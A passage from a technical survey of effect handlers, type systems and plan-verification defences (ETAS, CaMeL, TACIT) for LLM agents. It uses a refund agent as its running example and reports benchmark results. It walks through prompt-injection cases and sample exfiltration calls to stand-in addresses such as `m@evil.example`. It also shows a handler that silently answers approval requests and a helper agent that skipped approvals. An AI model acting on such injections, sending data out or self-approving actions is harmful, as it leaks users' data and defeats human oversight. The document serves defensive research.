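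McCann uses the union of permissions to determine what a combined program might request. If one step needs permission to read orders and the next needs permission to issue refunds, the sequence needs both. Pure code adds no permissions. A theorem called *no ambient effects* establishes that a program with no permissions can emit only observability messages, which report on its own execution. Before anyone runs a program, a reviewer can use the union to work out the most it could request. The intersection then determines how much of that it gets when another program calls it.

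### A simulated refund workload

McCann implemented a refund agent in this language and ran it on 200 simulated refund requests. The agent had access to email, customer records, the refund policy and a payment service. It produced 847 effect requests, a little over four per refund request. The runtime allowed 423 of them, denied 312 and escalated 112.

The denied requests were for refunds over the agent's limit or for customer records it was not authorised to see. The escalated requests were for amounts above the threshold for human approval. The three counts add up to 847, as they should if every request gets exactly one decision.

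The study shows that a developer can write a refund process entirely as effect requests, and that a runtime can sort them under a simple policy. This is useful to know because a language with no direct input or output might have been too restrictive for ordinary business software. The evidence about safety is much weaker. The runtime denied 37 percent of the effect requests, which is a lot for a routine task. The workload may have contained many improper requests, the agent may have been bad at following the policy, or it may have repeated requests after a refusal. McCann does not report the cause, or whether the denials and escalations were correct.

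There is also no comparison with the same agent in an ordinary framework, so the 312 denials don't show how many harmful actions the design prevented. An ordinary framework with a check inside its refund tool might have stopped many of the same requests. McCann, whose company makes the product, designed both the language and the test, so the test is unlikely to include a kind of effect that McCann overlooked when designing the language. A more informative experiment would have an outside team plant prompt injections in the agent's mailbox, then count the improper payments with and without the checkpoint.

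### Streams and very large requests

McCann acknowledges that one decision per request can be too coarse for programs that closely interleave computation and output, such as a stream in which every byte needs a check. Developers can choose how much a single request covers, but the runtime can't control anything smaller than a request. McCann leaves streaming to future work, describing it as a tradeoff between the size of each request and the delay each decision adds.

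Suppose the refund agent answers customers in a live chat, where words appear as the model produces them. If a single request covers the whole reply, the runtime has to decide before the text exists and can't stop the reply partway. If each word is a separate request, every word waits for a decision, and the rules can check only fragments. Swierstra's free-monad example divides output even further, displaying a file with a separate `PutChar` request for each character, so a checkpoint that screens for credit card numbers would receive one digit at a time. The rules could still find a card number if the context included the earlier characters, but by then most of the number would be on the screen. Holding back the reply until it is complete allows a proper check, but the customer no longer sees the words appear live.

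At the other extreme, a single request can cover too much. *Governed Metaprogramming for Intelligent Systems* warns of an "escape hatch" in systems that check effects but not the programs they generate. Such a system can generate a program without the original's constraints and run it instead. The paper proposes treating the execution of generated code as an effect that needs its own decision.

Shell commands, one of the 14 kinds of request in McCann's model, raise a similar problem. Programs at the lowest of Mashin's six trust levels can't request them, but others may need to. If the refund agent has that permission, it can request a command that runs a Python script, and the checkpoint receives the command as one piece of data. If the runtime allows the command, the script has all the ambient authority of an ordinary Python process, including the direct route to the payment provider.

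## Effect handlers: catching a request and choosing what happens

In McCann's language, one fixed runtime interprets every effect request. *Effect handlers* let programmers write the interpreter themselves, as ordinary code that they wrap around any part of a program. A handler catches requests from that part and determines what happens next, including whether the program resumes.

Most programmers know a limited kind of handler. When Python code raises an exception, the nearest surrounding `try` block catches it, and Python abandons the rest of the block. *Handling Algebraic Effects* (Plotkin and Pretnar, 2013) generalised exception handlers to other effects, such as reading input, printing and changing stored values. These handlers receive the request and its continuation (the rest of the program). If the handler calls the continuation with an answer, the program carries on as if its request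 had returned that answer. An exception is a request with no possible answer, so its handler can never resume the code that raised it.

Bauer and Pretnar (2012), in *Programming with Algebraic Effects and Handlers*, built a language called Eff around this idea. An Eff program *performs* an operation, which suspends the program until a handler supplies an answer. The rules for running a program inside a handler, which Bauer and Pretnar (2014), in *An Effect System for Algebraic Effects and Handlers*, set out step by step, cover three cases:

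1. If the program finishes, the handler receives its result and can transform it.
2. If the program performs an operation that the handler lists, the matching clause of the handler runs with the operation's argument and the continuation. The continuation runs inside the same handler, which therefore catches later requests too.
3. If the handler does not list the operation, the request travels outward to the next handler. When an answer comes back, the rest of the program still runs inside the first handler.

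### One refund program under four handlers

The following program handles the broken laptop. To keep it short, it fixes the steps that a model would normally choose:

```
settle(id):
    order = perform ReadOrder(id)
    reply = perform IssueRefund(id, order.total)
    if reply == "paid":
        perform SendEmail(order.customer, "Your refund is on its way.")
    else:
        perform SendEmail(order.customer, "A colleague will contact you.")
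```

Nothing in `settle` can reach the payment provider. Each handler below has a clause for every operation it catches, and `resume` calls the continuation with an answer:

```
real:
    ReadOrder(id)           -> resume(database.find(id))
    IssueRefund(id, amount) -> resume(provider.pay(id, amount))
    SendEmail(to, text)     -> resume(mail.send(to, text))

dry_run:
    IssueRefund(id, amount) -> show("refund", id, amount); resume("paid")
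    SendEmail(to, text)     -> show("email", to, text); resume("sent")

log:
    IssueRefund(id, amount) -> write_log(id, amount)
                               resume(perform IssueRefund(id, amount))

refuse:
    IssueRefund(id, amount) -> if amount > 500: resume("refused")
                               else: resume(perform IssueRefund(id, amount))
```

The company can now run the same program in four ways. In each line, the last handler named is the one closest to the program:

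```
with real:            settle("7731")
with real, dry_run:   settle("7731")
with real, log:       settle("7731")
with real, refuse:    settle("7731")
```

Under `real` alone, the provider pays 640 dollars and the customer receives the email. Under `dry_run`, the request to read the order passes outward to `real`, so the preview uses the true total. The screen shows the 640-dollar refund and the email, but neither goes out.

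The `log` handler writes a record and then performs the same request again. This does not loop forever because, in Plotkin and Pretnar's design, a handler does not catch requests made in its own clauses. The repeated request goes outward to `real`, which makes the payment. Under `refuse`, the program receives "refused" and sends the other email.

Bauer and Pretnar give a working equivalent of the dry run for printed output. Their handler intercepts the print requests of a program that prints "hello" and "world" and then computes 3 × 14. Nothing appears on the screen, and the result is 42 together with a list of the two words.

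A dry run depends on which operations the handler lists and on the simulated answers it returns. If `dry_run` did not list `SendEmail`, that request would pass outward to `real`, and the customer would get an email about a refund that was never made. Because `dry_run` always answers "paid", the preview never shows the email that follows a refusal.

A handler doesn't have to resume the program at once, or at all. If `refuse` left out `resume`, the program would stop at the refund and the customer would get no email. A handler can also store the continuation until a person approves the request. In Eff, it can resume the program several times. Bauer and Pretnar's example picks x as 10 or 20 and y as 0 or 5, then computes x − y. A handler that resumes with both answers to each choice returns all four results (10, 5, 20 and 15). Resuming more than once is useful for searching through possibilities,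 but if a handler resumed `settle` twice after the refund, the customer would get two emails.

Handlers can also carry information from one request to the next. Plotkin and Pretnar describe one that counts the characters a program has printed and suppresses output beyond a maximum. A similar handler could keep a running total of refunds for each order and so catch the two 320-dollar refunds. The printing handler lets the program continue as if the suppressed character had been printed, but a refund handler should report the refusal to the program. Otherwise the program will tell the customer to expect money that never arrives.

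### Why the nesting order matters

Suppose the company wants both the log and the refusal. It can nest them in either order:

```
with real, refuse, log:   settle("7731")    # log closest to the program
with real, log, refuse:   settle("7731")    # refusal closest to the program
```

In the first version, `log` catches the request for 640 dollars, records it and performs it again. The request then reaches `refuse`, which responds with "refused". In the second version, `refuse` catches the request first and responds, so `log` never receives it and the log stays empty. For a 40-dollar refund, the two versions behave identically, so tests with only small amounts would not reveal the difference.

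A log inside `refuse` records what the agent attempted, which helps identify an agent that keeps asking for too much. A log outside `refuse` records only the requests it let through, which is closer to what an accountant needs. A compliance team with the second log might conclude that the agent never tried to exceed its limit, even if it had.

The order of the `dry_run` and `refuse` handlers also matters. If `dry_run` is closest to the program, it responds with "paid" before `refuse` can check the amount, so the preview shows a refund that the live system would refuse. `dry_run` has to go outside `refuse` for the preview to be accurate.

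Bauer and Pretnar found similar traps in Eff. One of their programs places eight queens on a chessboard so that none attacks another, using a handler that goes back and tries a different square whenever the search gets stuck. If the list of placed queens is stored outside the handler, going back does not take a queen off the board, and the search fails. They conclude that although effects combine easily, "their combinations are not always easily understood".

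### Handlers for scripts that call language models

*Composable Effect Handling for Programming LLM-integrated Scripts* (Wang, 2025) brings handlers to ordinary Python. One example script asks a model for topics in a research area, then asks for a description of each. At about two seconds per call, running the calls one after another takes around 20 seconds. Wang treats model calls, logging and waiting as operations and wraps the unchanged script in handlers that run independent calls in parallel, which could cut the time to about five seconds. The same script can also run as a test without calling a model if one handler is replaced with another that supplies answers from a recorded run.

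Wang also measured a larger program for Tree of Thoughts, a method in which a model proposes several partial solutions, scores them and continues from the best. The task was to combine four numbers with arithmetic to make 24. On three puzzles, parallel handlers cut the running time from 413–465 seconds to 34–37 seconds. That is 11 to 13 times faster, although Wang reports an average of 10.88. The gain comes from running model calls at the same time. A programmer could also do this by hand, but handlers make it possible without rewriting the search program.

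Parallel execution can change the order in which effects happen. Wang therefore includes a handler that lets model calls finish in any order but makes each printed result wait for the one before it. An agent that must ask for approval before it pays would need a similar constraint on order.

In Wang's scripts, the program performs the operations and the model only returns answers. *Sharing State Between Prompts and Programs* (Cheng, Weber and colleagues, 2025) describes Nightjar, a system in which the model can request operations itself. A Python program can contain a prompt, and the model evaluating that prompt can request to read or change the program's variables or to jump to another point in the program. In one example, a loop answers questions about a graph of paper citations until the user types "Exit, please." The model requests the user's message, and a handler supplies it and resumes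 the model. When the model then requests to leave the loop, the handler moves the program past the loop and does not resume the model.

Cheng and colleagues describe effects and handlers as a generalisation of tool use. Nightjar's handlers can also cancel the model's evaluation, which the code behind an ordinary tool call can't do. Similarly, `refuse` could end a refund program by leaving out `resume`.

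Compared with programs that pass data to and from the model by hand, Nightjar programs needed 39.6 percent fewer lines on average and reached comparable accuracy or improved it by 4 to 19 percent. They took between 0.4 and 4.3 times as long to run. The design has a safety drawback, because a prompt can refer to any variable in scope. If the 500-dollar limit were one of those variables, the model could issue a request to change it, and a handler would have to forbid that request explicitly.

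### Why handlers alone are not a security boundary

Wang's handlers are meant to make scripts modular and fast, and they do not confine hostile code. A Python script running under them can still call `requests.post` directly. The same is true of other languages that add handlers but keep their existing built-in functions. Debian's *tutorial.ml*, an OCaml test program, defines an operation `Print` and several handlers for it. One handler performs it by calling OCaml's built-in `print_string`. Any other code could also call `print_string`, and no handler would catch the call.

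Eff is stricter, because all its effects go through operations, but a handler still doesn't catch operations it doesn't list. A request that no handler catches reaches the top level of the program, where built-in code performs the real input or output. If the refund company added an operation `IssueVoucher` and forgot to update `refuse`, the program could issue vouchers of any value, provided that the top level had code for issuing them. A safer top level would reject every operation that the policy does not list.

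Code inside the company's handlers can also install handlers of its own, and these catch requests first. Suppose that a person must approve large refunds through an operation `AskApproval`, and a model writes this:

```
with say_yes:
    if perform AskApproval("7731", 640):
        perform IssueRefund("7731", 640)
```

If `say_yes` catches `AskApproval` and resumes with `true`, no member of staff sees the request for approval, and the program goes on to request the refund as if someone had agreed. An outer handler still receives the refund request, but it can stop the payment only if it keeps its own record of approvals and checks that record instead of relying on the program.

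If operations are the only way to cause an effect, an inner handler cannot pay anyone by itself, because its own requests also travel outward. The natural place for a checkpoint is therefore outermost, directly around the code that carries out effects. *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* (McCann, 2026) models a checkpoint this way, as a machine-checked wrapper around a handler. But a checkpoint there does not receive requests that an inner handler has already answered, such as the approval request above.

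Types do not fill this gap. The types in the first version of Eff did not record effects. In their 2014 paper, Bauer and Pretnar extended each program's type to `A ! Δ`, where A is the type of the result and Δ is the set of operations the program might perform. They proved that if a program with this type stops at an operation, the operation is in Δ. But when a handler catches an operation, their system can remove it from Δ, so a program that changes stored values counts as having no effects if a handler catches every read and write.

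Effekt's *An Introduction to (Algebraic) Effect Handlers* gives the example of a function that searches for three numbers with a given sum. Its type includes the effects `{ Flip, Fail }`. Wrapping it in handlers for both effects gives a function whose type has an empty effect set, `{}`.

This makes sense if the list is meant to show callers which operations they still have to handle, but it is a poor record of what the program requested. Inside `dry_run`, `settle` has the same effects in its type as a program that never requests a refund. Checking the type would therefore not catch a violation of a rule that an agent must not even request refunds. The refund would then go through once someone removed the dry run.

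### How ETAS keeps handled requests visible

ETAS, the agent language by Tan and colleagues, addresses this last problem by tracking two things for each piece of code. The *escaping effects* are the operations that may reach the caller unhandled, as in other effect systems. The *request summary* describes every sequence of operations the code may request, including operations a handler catches.

Their main example is a workflow that reviews code changes. A reviewer agent has one tool, which reads source files, and proposes a patch. A second function asks a person to approve the patch and then applies it to the repository. In simplified notation:

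```
rule ApprovedApply:  Approval.request >> Repo.apply

apply(patch), which must obey ApprovedApply:
    if perform Approval.request(patch):
        perform Repo.apply(patch)

main(diff):
    patch = Reviewer(diff)
    with DryRun: apply(patch)
```

The symbol `>>` means that an approval request must come before any request to apply a patch. A separate rule, `ReviewOnly`, limits the reviewer to querying the model and reading the repository. `DryRun` catches `Repo.apply` and resumes at once without changing any files.

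Suppose a block of code has escaping effects ε. If a handler catches the operations H, and its own clauses may perform εₕ, the wrapped block has escaping effects (ε \ H) ∪ εₕ. For `apply`, ε contains `Approval.request` and `Repo.apply`, and `DryRun` removes `Repo.apply`. The request summary keeps both, because the compiler never deletes a block's own requests when it processes a handler. It adds any requests that the handler's clauses might make and allows for runs that end early.

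A summary can show policy violations that escaping effects don't. If a developer adds a write to the reviewer and wraps it in `DryRun`, the reviewer's escaping effects stay the same, but its summary now contains a write, which `ReviewOnly` forbids. If the developer moves `Repo.apply` ahead of the approval request, the types and escaping effects stay the same, but the order in the summary violates `ApprovedApply`.

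To check the order, the compiler turns the rule into a small table of states, known as a security automaton. Every run begins in the state "start", and each request moves it to another state:

| Current state | After an approval request | After a write request |
|---|---|---|
| start | asked | violated |
| asked | asked | asked |
| violated | violated | violated |

The compiler runs every sequence in the summary through this table. As written, `apply` can produce an approval request alone, or an approval request followed by a write. Both end in "asked", which proves that the function obeys the rule. If the two operations are swapped, every complete run ends in "violated", so the compiler rejects the program.

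The compiler can't always tell whether a program will break the rule. If one branch asks first and the other writes first, the possible final states are "asked" and "violated", and the compiler may not know which branch will run. It accepts the program but keeps a *residual monitor*, which follows the same table during the run and stops the program at the first forbidden request. The summary includes both branches even if one can never run, so the compiler sometimes keeps a monitor it doesn't need. An unneeded monitor takes some extra time but doesn't let a violation through.

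ETAS also changes the order of steps at run time. The monitor checks each request before the language looks for a handler, so an inner handler cannot hide a request from the monitor. If no handler catches the request, the *host*, the trusted software that carries out effects, then checks that the operation is among the function's declared effects and that the host's own permission rules allow this particular request.

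The monitors also stay active when one agent calls another. Tan and colleagues cite a bug in Goose, an open-source agent, in which a parent session required approval for sensitive tools, but a helper agent started in automatic mode and ran tools without asking the parent's user. In ETAS, calling a function adds its monitor to those of its callers, and every request must satisfy all of them, so the parent's rule still applies even if the helper's is looser.

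### What the approval rule leaves unchecked

`ApprovedApply` requires a request for approval but does not require that the request be granted. In the example, the `if` statement checks the answer. If a developer removed the `if`, the program would still request approval, but it would request the write even after a refusal. The compiler would accept this because the sequence would still be an approval request followed by a write.

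The rule also covers only the names and order of operations, not their arguments. After one approval request, the table permits any number of writes, so a person could approve a change to one file and the program could then request changes to ten others without breaking the rule. A handler like `say_yes` would also satisfy the rule, because the monitor records the approval request before the handler answers it.

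Tan and colleagues leave these matters to the host, whose permission check can examine the arguments and the history of the run. For example, it can confirm that a person consented to this exact patch. The refund agent's 500-dollar limit would also belong in the permission check, since the ordering rules cannot distinguish a refund of 40 dollars from one of 640. A developer could define separate operations for small and large refunds, but then other code would have to sort every refund correctly.

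ETAS comes with proofs that, in every finite run, the requests it admits obey the ordering rules, and that the host carries out only operations among the declared escaping effects. The proofs assume complete mediation and no unreported effects from the host's operations, so shell commands are a problem, as they are in McCann's design.

### How Tan and colleagues tested ETAS

For the safety tests, Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent called Nomo in ETAS and examined the part that chooses which files to read or search. They ran ten scenarios with scripted model replies and tool results. Four finished normally, six stopped where they should have, and all 19 requests were handled as expected.

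They also gave the compiler six short programs based on the patch example. It accepted the two valid programs and rejected the four with deliberate faults: a missing approval request, an approval request after the write, a forbidden write inside a dry run, and an undeclared write. A separate Python model of the rule language matched a direct reading of the rules in all 419,712 comparisons.

These tests produced no mismatches, which is good evidence that the rules mean what Tan and colleagues intended and that the prototype applies them correctly in simple cases. They are weak evidence of how well it resists attacks, because Tan and colleagues wrote both the language and the test programs, and the scripted replies did not include a model trying to get around the rules. The tests also did not measure how often a real agent would attempt a forbidden action.

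In tests on 26 synthetic workflows based on patterns in open-source agents, the compiler's optimisations reduced execution time by 23.2 percent. The baseline was the same ETAS programs without optimisation, so the result doesn't show that ETAS is faster than Python. The tests also used a scripted host to exclude model and network delays, so an agent that waits two seconds for each reply, like Wang's script, would gain much less overall.

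In another test, on 12 synthetic workflows with a real model, the compiler cut input tokens (the units of text that a model processes and providers charge for) by 67.8 percent. It shortened the conversation history and left out tools, data fields and source code that the task did not need. The baseline always sent all of this material, so an agent whose developers had already trimmed its prompts would save fewer tokens. The 67.8 percent figure covers only workflows that gave correct results both with and without the reductions, and each workflow ran once per setting. Across all settings, five of the 72 runs failed.

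Tan and colleagues also let two agents revise their own prompts and code over five generations. The compiler checked each revision against fixed types, effect limits and ordering rules before it could run. Within these constraints, accuracy rose from 69.9 to 78.9 percent on 256 financial questions and from 30 to 72 percent on 50 patent questions.

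## Checking generated code before it runs

The ETAS compiler checks programs written in a language designed for agents. Other researchers also check code before it runs, but theirs is code that a model writes during a task. The runtime executes it only if it passes. Rice's theorem implies that a safe checker must reject some harmless code. Designs differ in what they check and in whether the model must write the whole program before seeing any data.

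### Verifying a whole plan

In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), Meijer considers an email assistant with tools for fetching and sending mail. A user asks for a summary of the inbox, and one of the messages contains an instruction to send that summary to an outside address without telling the user. An agent that picks each tool call after reading the previous result may comply.

Meijer's remedy is for the model to write the complete workflow before it fetches anything. Steps refer to earlier results by name, as in this simplified version:

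```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize_emails(emails)
return summary
```

The model hasn't read any mail when it writes the workflow, so a planted message cannot add a step that sends email. But a hostile instruction can reach the model earlier, through a tool's description or the user's own request. Meijer gives an example of each, and in both, the workflow gains an extra line such as `send_email("backup@outside.example", summary)`.

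A verifier therefore checks the workflow before it runs. Under one of Meijer's rules, a workflow fails if data can get from a source (the result of fetching mail) to a sink (the body of any email to an address outside the company). Static analysis tools such as CodeQL look for these paths by tracing which values each step uses. Here `summary` depends on `emails` and ends up in an outside email, so the verifier rejects the workflow before any step runs.

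A blocking monitor would also stop that email, but only after the earlier steps had run. This matters most when those steps have effects of their own. If a workflow pays a refund and then tries to send a forbidden email, a monitor leaves the job half done, whereas a verifier rejects the workflow before it pays the refund.

### Specifying what must not change

A verifier can also check whether a workflow achieves the right result. In Meijer's example, a user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the deletion tool accepts patterns. The model writes `delete_file("*.txt")` because one step is shorter than two, but this deletes every text file.

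Suppose the specification is a *postcondition*, a statement that must be true when the workflow ends:

```
foo.txt ∉ files  and  bar.txt ∉ files
```

The one-step workflow satisfies this specification because it deletes both files. A verifier would approve it, even though it would also delete all the user's other text files. The specification lacks a *frame condition*, which states what has to stay the same. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described the underlying difficulty, the frame problem, in 1969.

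Meijer adds a frame condition to the tool's contract: `delete_file` removes every file that matches the pattern and leaves all others as they were. This alone does not rule out `*.txt`, because the specification of the request still demands only that two files disappear. The request needs a frame condition as well:

```
for every file f other than foo.txt and bar.txt:
    f exists afterwards if and only if f existed before
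```

The verifier now rejects deleting `*.txt`, since there might be a third text file, and accepts two separate deletions. It can accept them only because the tool's frame condition guarantees that deleting `foo.txt` doesn't affect other files. A refund agent's postcondition can be too weak in the same way, since "the customer has received 640 dollars for order 7731" also permits a workflow that refunds ten other orders.

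In a later talk, written up in AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), Meijer proposes that the model supply a proof with its plan. The plan is a free monad, so each request includes the rest of the program. In the example, a plan can finish, read a file or delete a file. The property `NoDeletion` has proof rules for finishing and reading but none for deleting, so a plan that contains a deletion cannot have a proof. If the plan reads a file, the proof must cover every text the file might contain, since the next step may depend on it. A proof can be hard to find, but checking it is mechanical, so nobody has to trust the model that wrote it. The proof would not help if the interpreter deleted files while carrying out a read.

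### CaMeL's two models and its interpreter

Meijer wrote in 2025 that nobody had formally measured how planning before acting affects an agent's usefulness. Measurements now exist for CaMeL, the system Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025).

CaMeL uses two language models. A privileged model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions, and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. It never reads emails, web pages or other outside data. A quarantined model reads that data and extracts values from it, but it has no tools. An interpreter runs the plan and calls the tools. For a refund agent that a staff member asks to deal with the latest complaint, the plan might be:

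```python
email = read_latest_email()
order_id = ask_quarantined_model("Find the order number", email)
order = read_order(order_id)
if order.condition == "broken":
    issue_refund(order_id, order.total)
```

A fake staff note in the email cannot add a step to this plan. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, call this property *control-flow integrity*, meaning that the choice and order of tool calls follow a plan that depends only on trusted information. Outside data can determine which branch of the plan runs, but it cannot add a branch.

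The email can still change the values in the plan. If planted text makes the quarantined model return a different order number, the agent refunds the wrong order. Willison proposed the two-model design in 2023 and acknowledged this flaw in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025).

CaMeL's interpreter therefore tags every value with its sources and with the people who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their tags, so `order_id` counts as untrusted because it comes from `email`. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a Python function that inspects the arguments and their tags and allows or refuses the call. (Debenedetti and colleagues call the tags capabilities. In the older sense of the word, a capability is an unforgeable value that grants a permission, whereas these tags describe data.)

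A policy that refuses refunds on untrusted order numbers would stop the attack, but it would also block refunds for every honest customer who sends an order number by email. A policy that checks whether the order belongs to the sender would be more useful.

CaMeL fixes the plan in advance but checks its policies only when the plan reaches a tool call. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) also checks the whole plan before it starts. It converts the plan into a finite set of states, each labelled with facts such as which tools have already run and whether an argument came from an untrusted source. A program called a model checker then explores every path through the states. One rule requires an agent to have the incident team's approval before it cuts a computer off from the network. If a path breaks this rule, the checker returns that path, and the privileged model can repair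 the plan. To keep the number of states finite, the conversion assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times, so the checker sometimes rejects a safe plan.

### Results on AgentDojo

Most of these defences have been tested on AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It has 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: banking, an office workspace with email and files, the messaging service Slack, and travel booking. It also has 35 attacker goals, and it plants instructions for carrying them out in data that the agent reads. Each attack trial pairs a user task with an attacker goal from the same setting. The benchmark scores whether the agent completed the task and whether the attacker's goal was achieved.

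*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) reprints CaMeL's published results for two models. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, CaMeL completed between 62.5 and 81.4 percent of tasks, depending on the setting, and one of 963 attacks succeeded. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, no attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only about half the tasks in three settings and 1.4 percent in the travel setting.

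Scores for attack resistance and task completion have to be read together, because an agent that does nothing also resists every attack. *SecureClaw* (2026) reran CaMeL and found that none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks even without an attack. *MetaPermit* (2026) traces much of CaMeL's low attack success rate to unfinished work. The privileged model has to write one well-formed program for the whole task, and in many runs the program was valid but incomplete. The problem is worst with small models. In one case in *CapLite* (2026), CaMeL queried a 1.7-billion-parameter model 30 times without running any tools.

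CaMeL also uses more tokens than an undefended agent. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) measured 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens on the median task. All these reruns come from papers that propose competing defences, and adapting CaMeL to a new test setup may have lowered its scores. The reruns still agree with the published results on the main point, that very few attacks succeed and many tasks remain unfinished.

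### The cost of planning before seeing the data

A plan written in advance needs a branch for everything the data might reveal. If a complaint turns out to concern two orders and the plan handles only one, the agent cannot add the other. The problem is worst when the data contains the steps to follow, as when a user asks an agent to carry out the instructions in an attached form. The user then wants outside text to determine the agent's actions, which CaMeL is designed to prevent.

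*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) reports how much longer plans become when agents operate a desktop computer through screenshots. CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo averaged 52 lines, with about five tool calls and four branches. The paper's plans for desktop agents averaged 213 lines, with 41 tool calls and 40 branches, and roughly half of each plan never ran. On OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks, the paper's design kept up to 57 percent of the performance of leading models.

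The extra branches also give attackers more targets. Many plans include a branch that closes cookie banners. Foerster and colleagues put a fake banner inside an advertisement, and the agent's attempt to close it opened the attacker's site. Control-flow integrity did not stop the attack because every click was part of the plan.

The guarantee also doesn't carry over from one agent to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents and asked it to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack. The database contained a planted instruction to email the data to an outsider. The agent that queried the database and the coordinating agent both treated this text as data, but the coordinating agent then pasted the summary into its instructions to the messaging agent. That agent's privileged model read the planted text as part of a trusted request and added the email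 to its plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by passing instructions and data through separate channels. On their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, 12.9 percent of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with separate CaMeL agents and none with the new protocol.

### A leak that run-time tags miss

CaMeL's tags have a gap even within one agent. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, demonstrate it with a program that reveals whether a secret bank balance is above some threshold. In outline:

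```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the interpreter sets `tmp` to false and tags it as secret. The assignment `rich = False` then doesn't run, so `rich` is still true and still has its public tag. The policy allows the email, which gives away the secret. The interpreter tracks only the steps that run, so it misses the information revealed by the skipped assignment.

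Garby and colleagues also found that turning on CaMeL's policies halves the number of banking tasks it completes. They propose instead a small language that labels every value, with a machine-checked proof about how labelled information can flow. An agent written in it completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL does without policies, and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

A type checker can also close this gap, because it examines every branch of a program, including the ones that a particular run skips.

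### Capabilities tracked in types

Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, which checks code written in the programming language Scala 3. The agent sends a snippet, the compiler checks it, and the runtime executes it if it passes. The agent reads the result before writing the next snippet, so it can adjust its approach if the data is unexpected.

In TACIT, code needs a capability for every effect. Code that holds a `FileSystem` value, for example, can open files in one directory. Each value's type includes a *capture set*, which lists the capabilities the value may use. If `f` is a file, the function `s => f.write(s)` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, which means it takes text, returns no useful value and may use `f`. A function of type `String -> Unit` has an empty capture set, so it is pure and cannot write, print or send anything.

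TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`, which the agent cannot open. The agent can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the secret and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions, so the compiler accepts this snippet:

```scala
val key = readClassified("github.txt")
key.map(k => k.length)
```

It rejects this one:

```scala
val key = readClassified("github.txt")
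key.map(k => println(k))
```

Printing requires a capability, so the second function's capture set is not empty. An agent wrote a longer version of this line during the tests. In the accepted snippet, the length stays wrapped. An agent that prints it sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the number through a separate channel. The trick with `rich` fails because comparing a classified balance with a threshold gives a classified result, which an `if` outside the wrapper cannot use. When the agent needs a summary of a secret document, it can send the wrapped text to a separate, trusted model, which returns a wrapped summary.

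Permissions also expire. A call to `requestFileSystem` creates a `FileSystem` capability for a single block of code. An agent might try to keep it by returning a function that reads a file later:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("notes.txt").read()
}
```

The function's capture set contains `fs`, which does not exist outside the block, so the compiler rejects the code. A file path may be unknown until the program runs, so TACIT compares paths with the permitted directory at run time instead of relying on types.

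These checks work only if the language gives code no way to bypass them, such as Haskell's `unsafePerformIO`. TACIT compiles agent code in a safe mode that forbids unchecked type conversions, runtime type inspection and libraries with untracked effects. The compiler, TACIT's library and the runtime all belong to the trusted computing base. The guarantee doesn't cover timing leaks or anything done by external programs that the agent starts.

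### How well TACIT worked

For the main safety test, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of secrets. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user's own request was malicious. The user asked for secrets directly in five of these and used a pretext in six, such as posing as an administrator who needed to replace passwords. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets in `Classified` and once with them as plain text. The table gives the percentage of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

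| Model | With types, all 131 trials | Without types, all 131 | Without types, 120 injections | Without types, 11 malicious requests |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100 | 98.5 | 100 | 81.8 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100 | 91.6 | 97.5 | 27.3 |

Most of the difference comes from the 11 malicious requests. Without the types, MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in eight of those requests and in three of the 120 injection trials, while Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every injection. The result supports the claim that the types work whatever the model does, but 11 requests are too few to estimate how often a model would leak in practice. The types did not make the agents less useful. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2 percent of the ordinary tasks with them and 83.3 percent without them. The lower rate is partly because it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

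Odersky and colleagues also tested whether writing Scala makes agents worse at their jobs. τ²-bench simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, and its scores are percentages of tasks solved:

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
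| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7 percent with Scala and 43.3 percent with ordinary tools, a difference of five faults. At most 8 percent of the τ²-bench snippets needed a second attempt at compiling. These are good results for a language feature that is still experimental and rare in training data. But they measure the effect of writing Scala, not of a strict policy, because the τ²-bench agents could use the same operations either way.

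The AgentDojo results say more about that cost. Odersky and colleagues moved all four settings to TACIT and ran the two models from CaMeL's published results. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed:

| Model and system | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 52.8 | 53.8 | 48.6 | 1.4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 56.9 | 50.5 | 40.0 | 64.3 |
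| o4-mini-high, CaMeL | 62.5 | 81.4 | 68.6 | 74.3 |
| o4-mini-high, TACIT | 59.0 | 52.9 | 47.6 | 68.6 |

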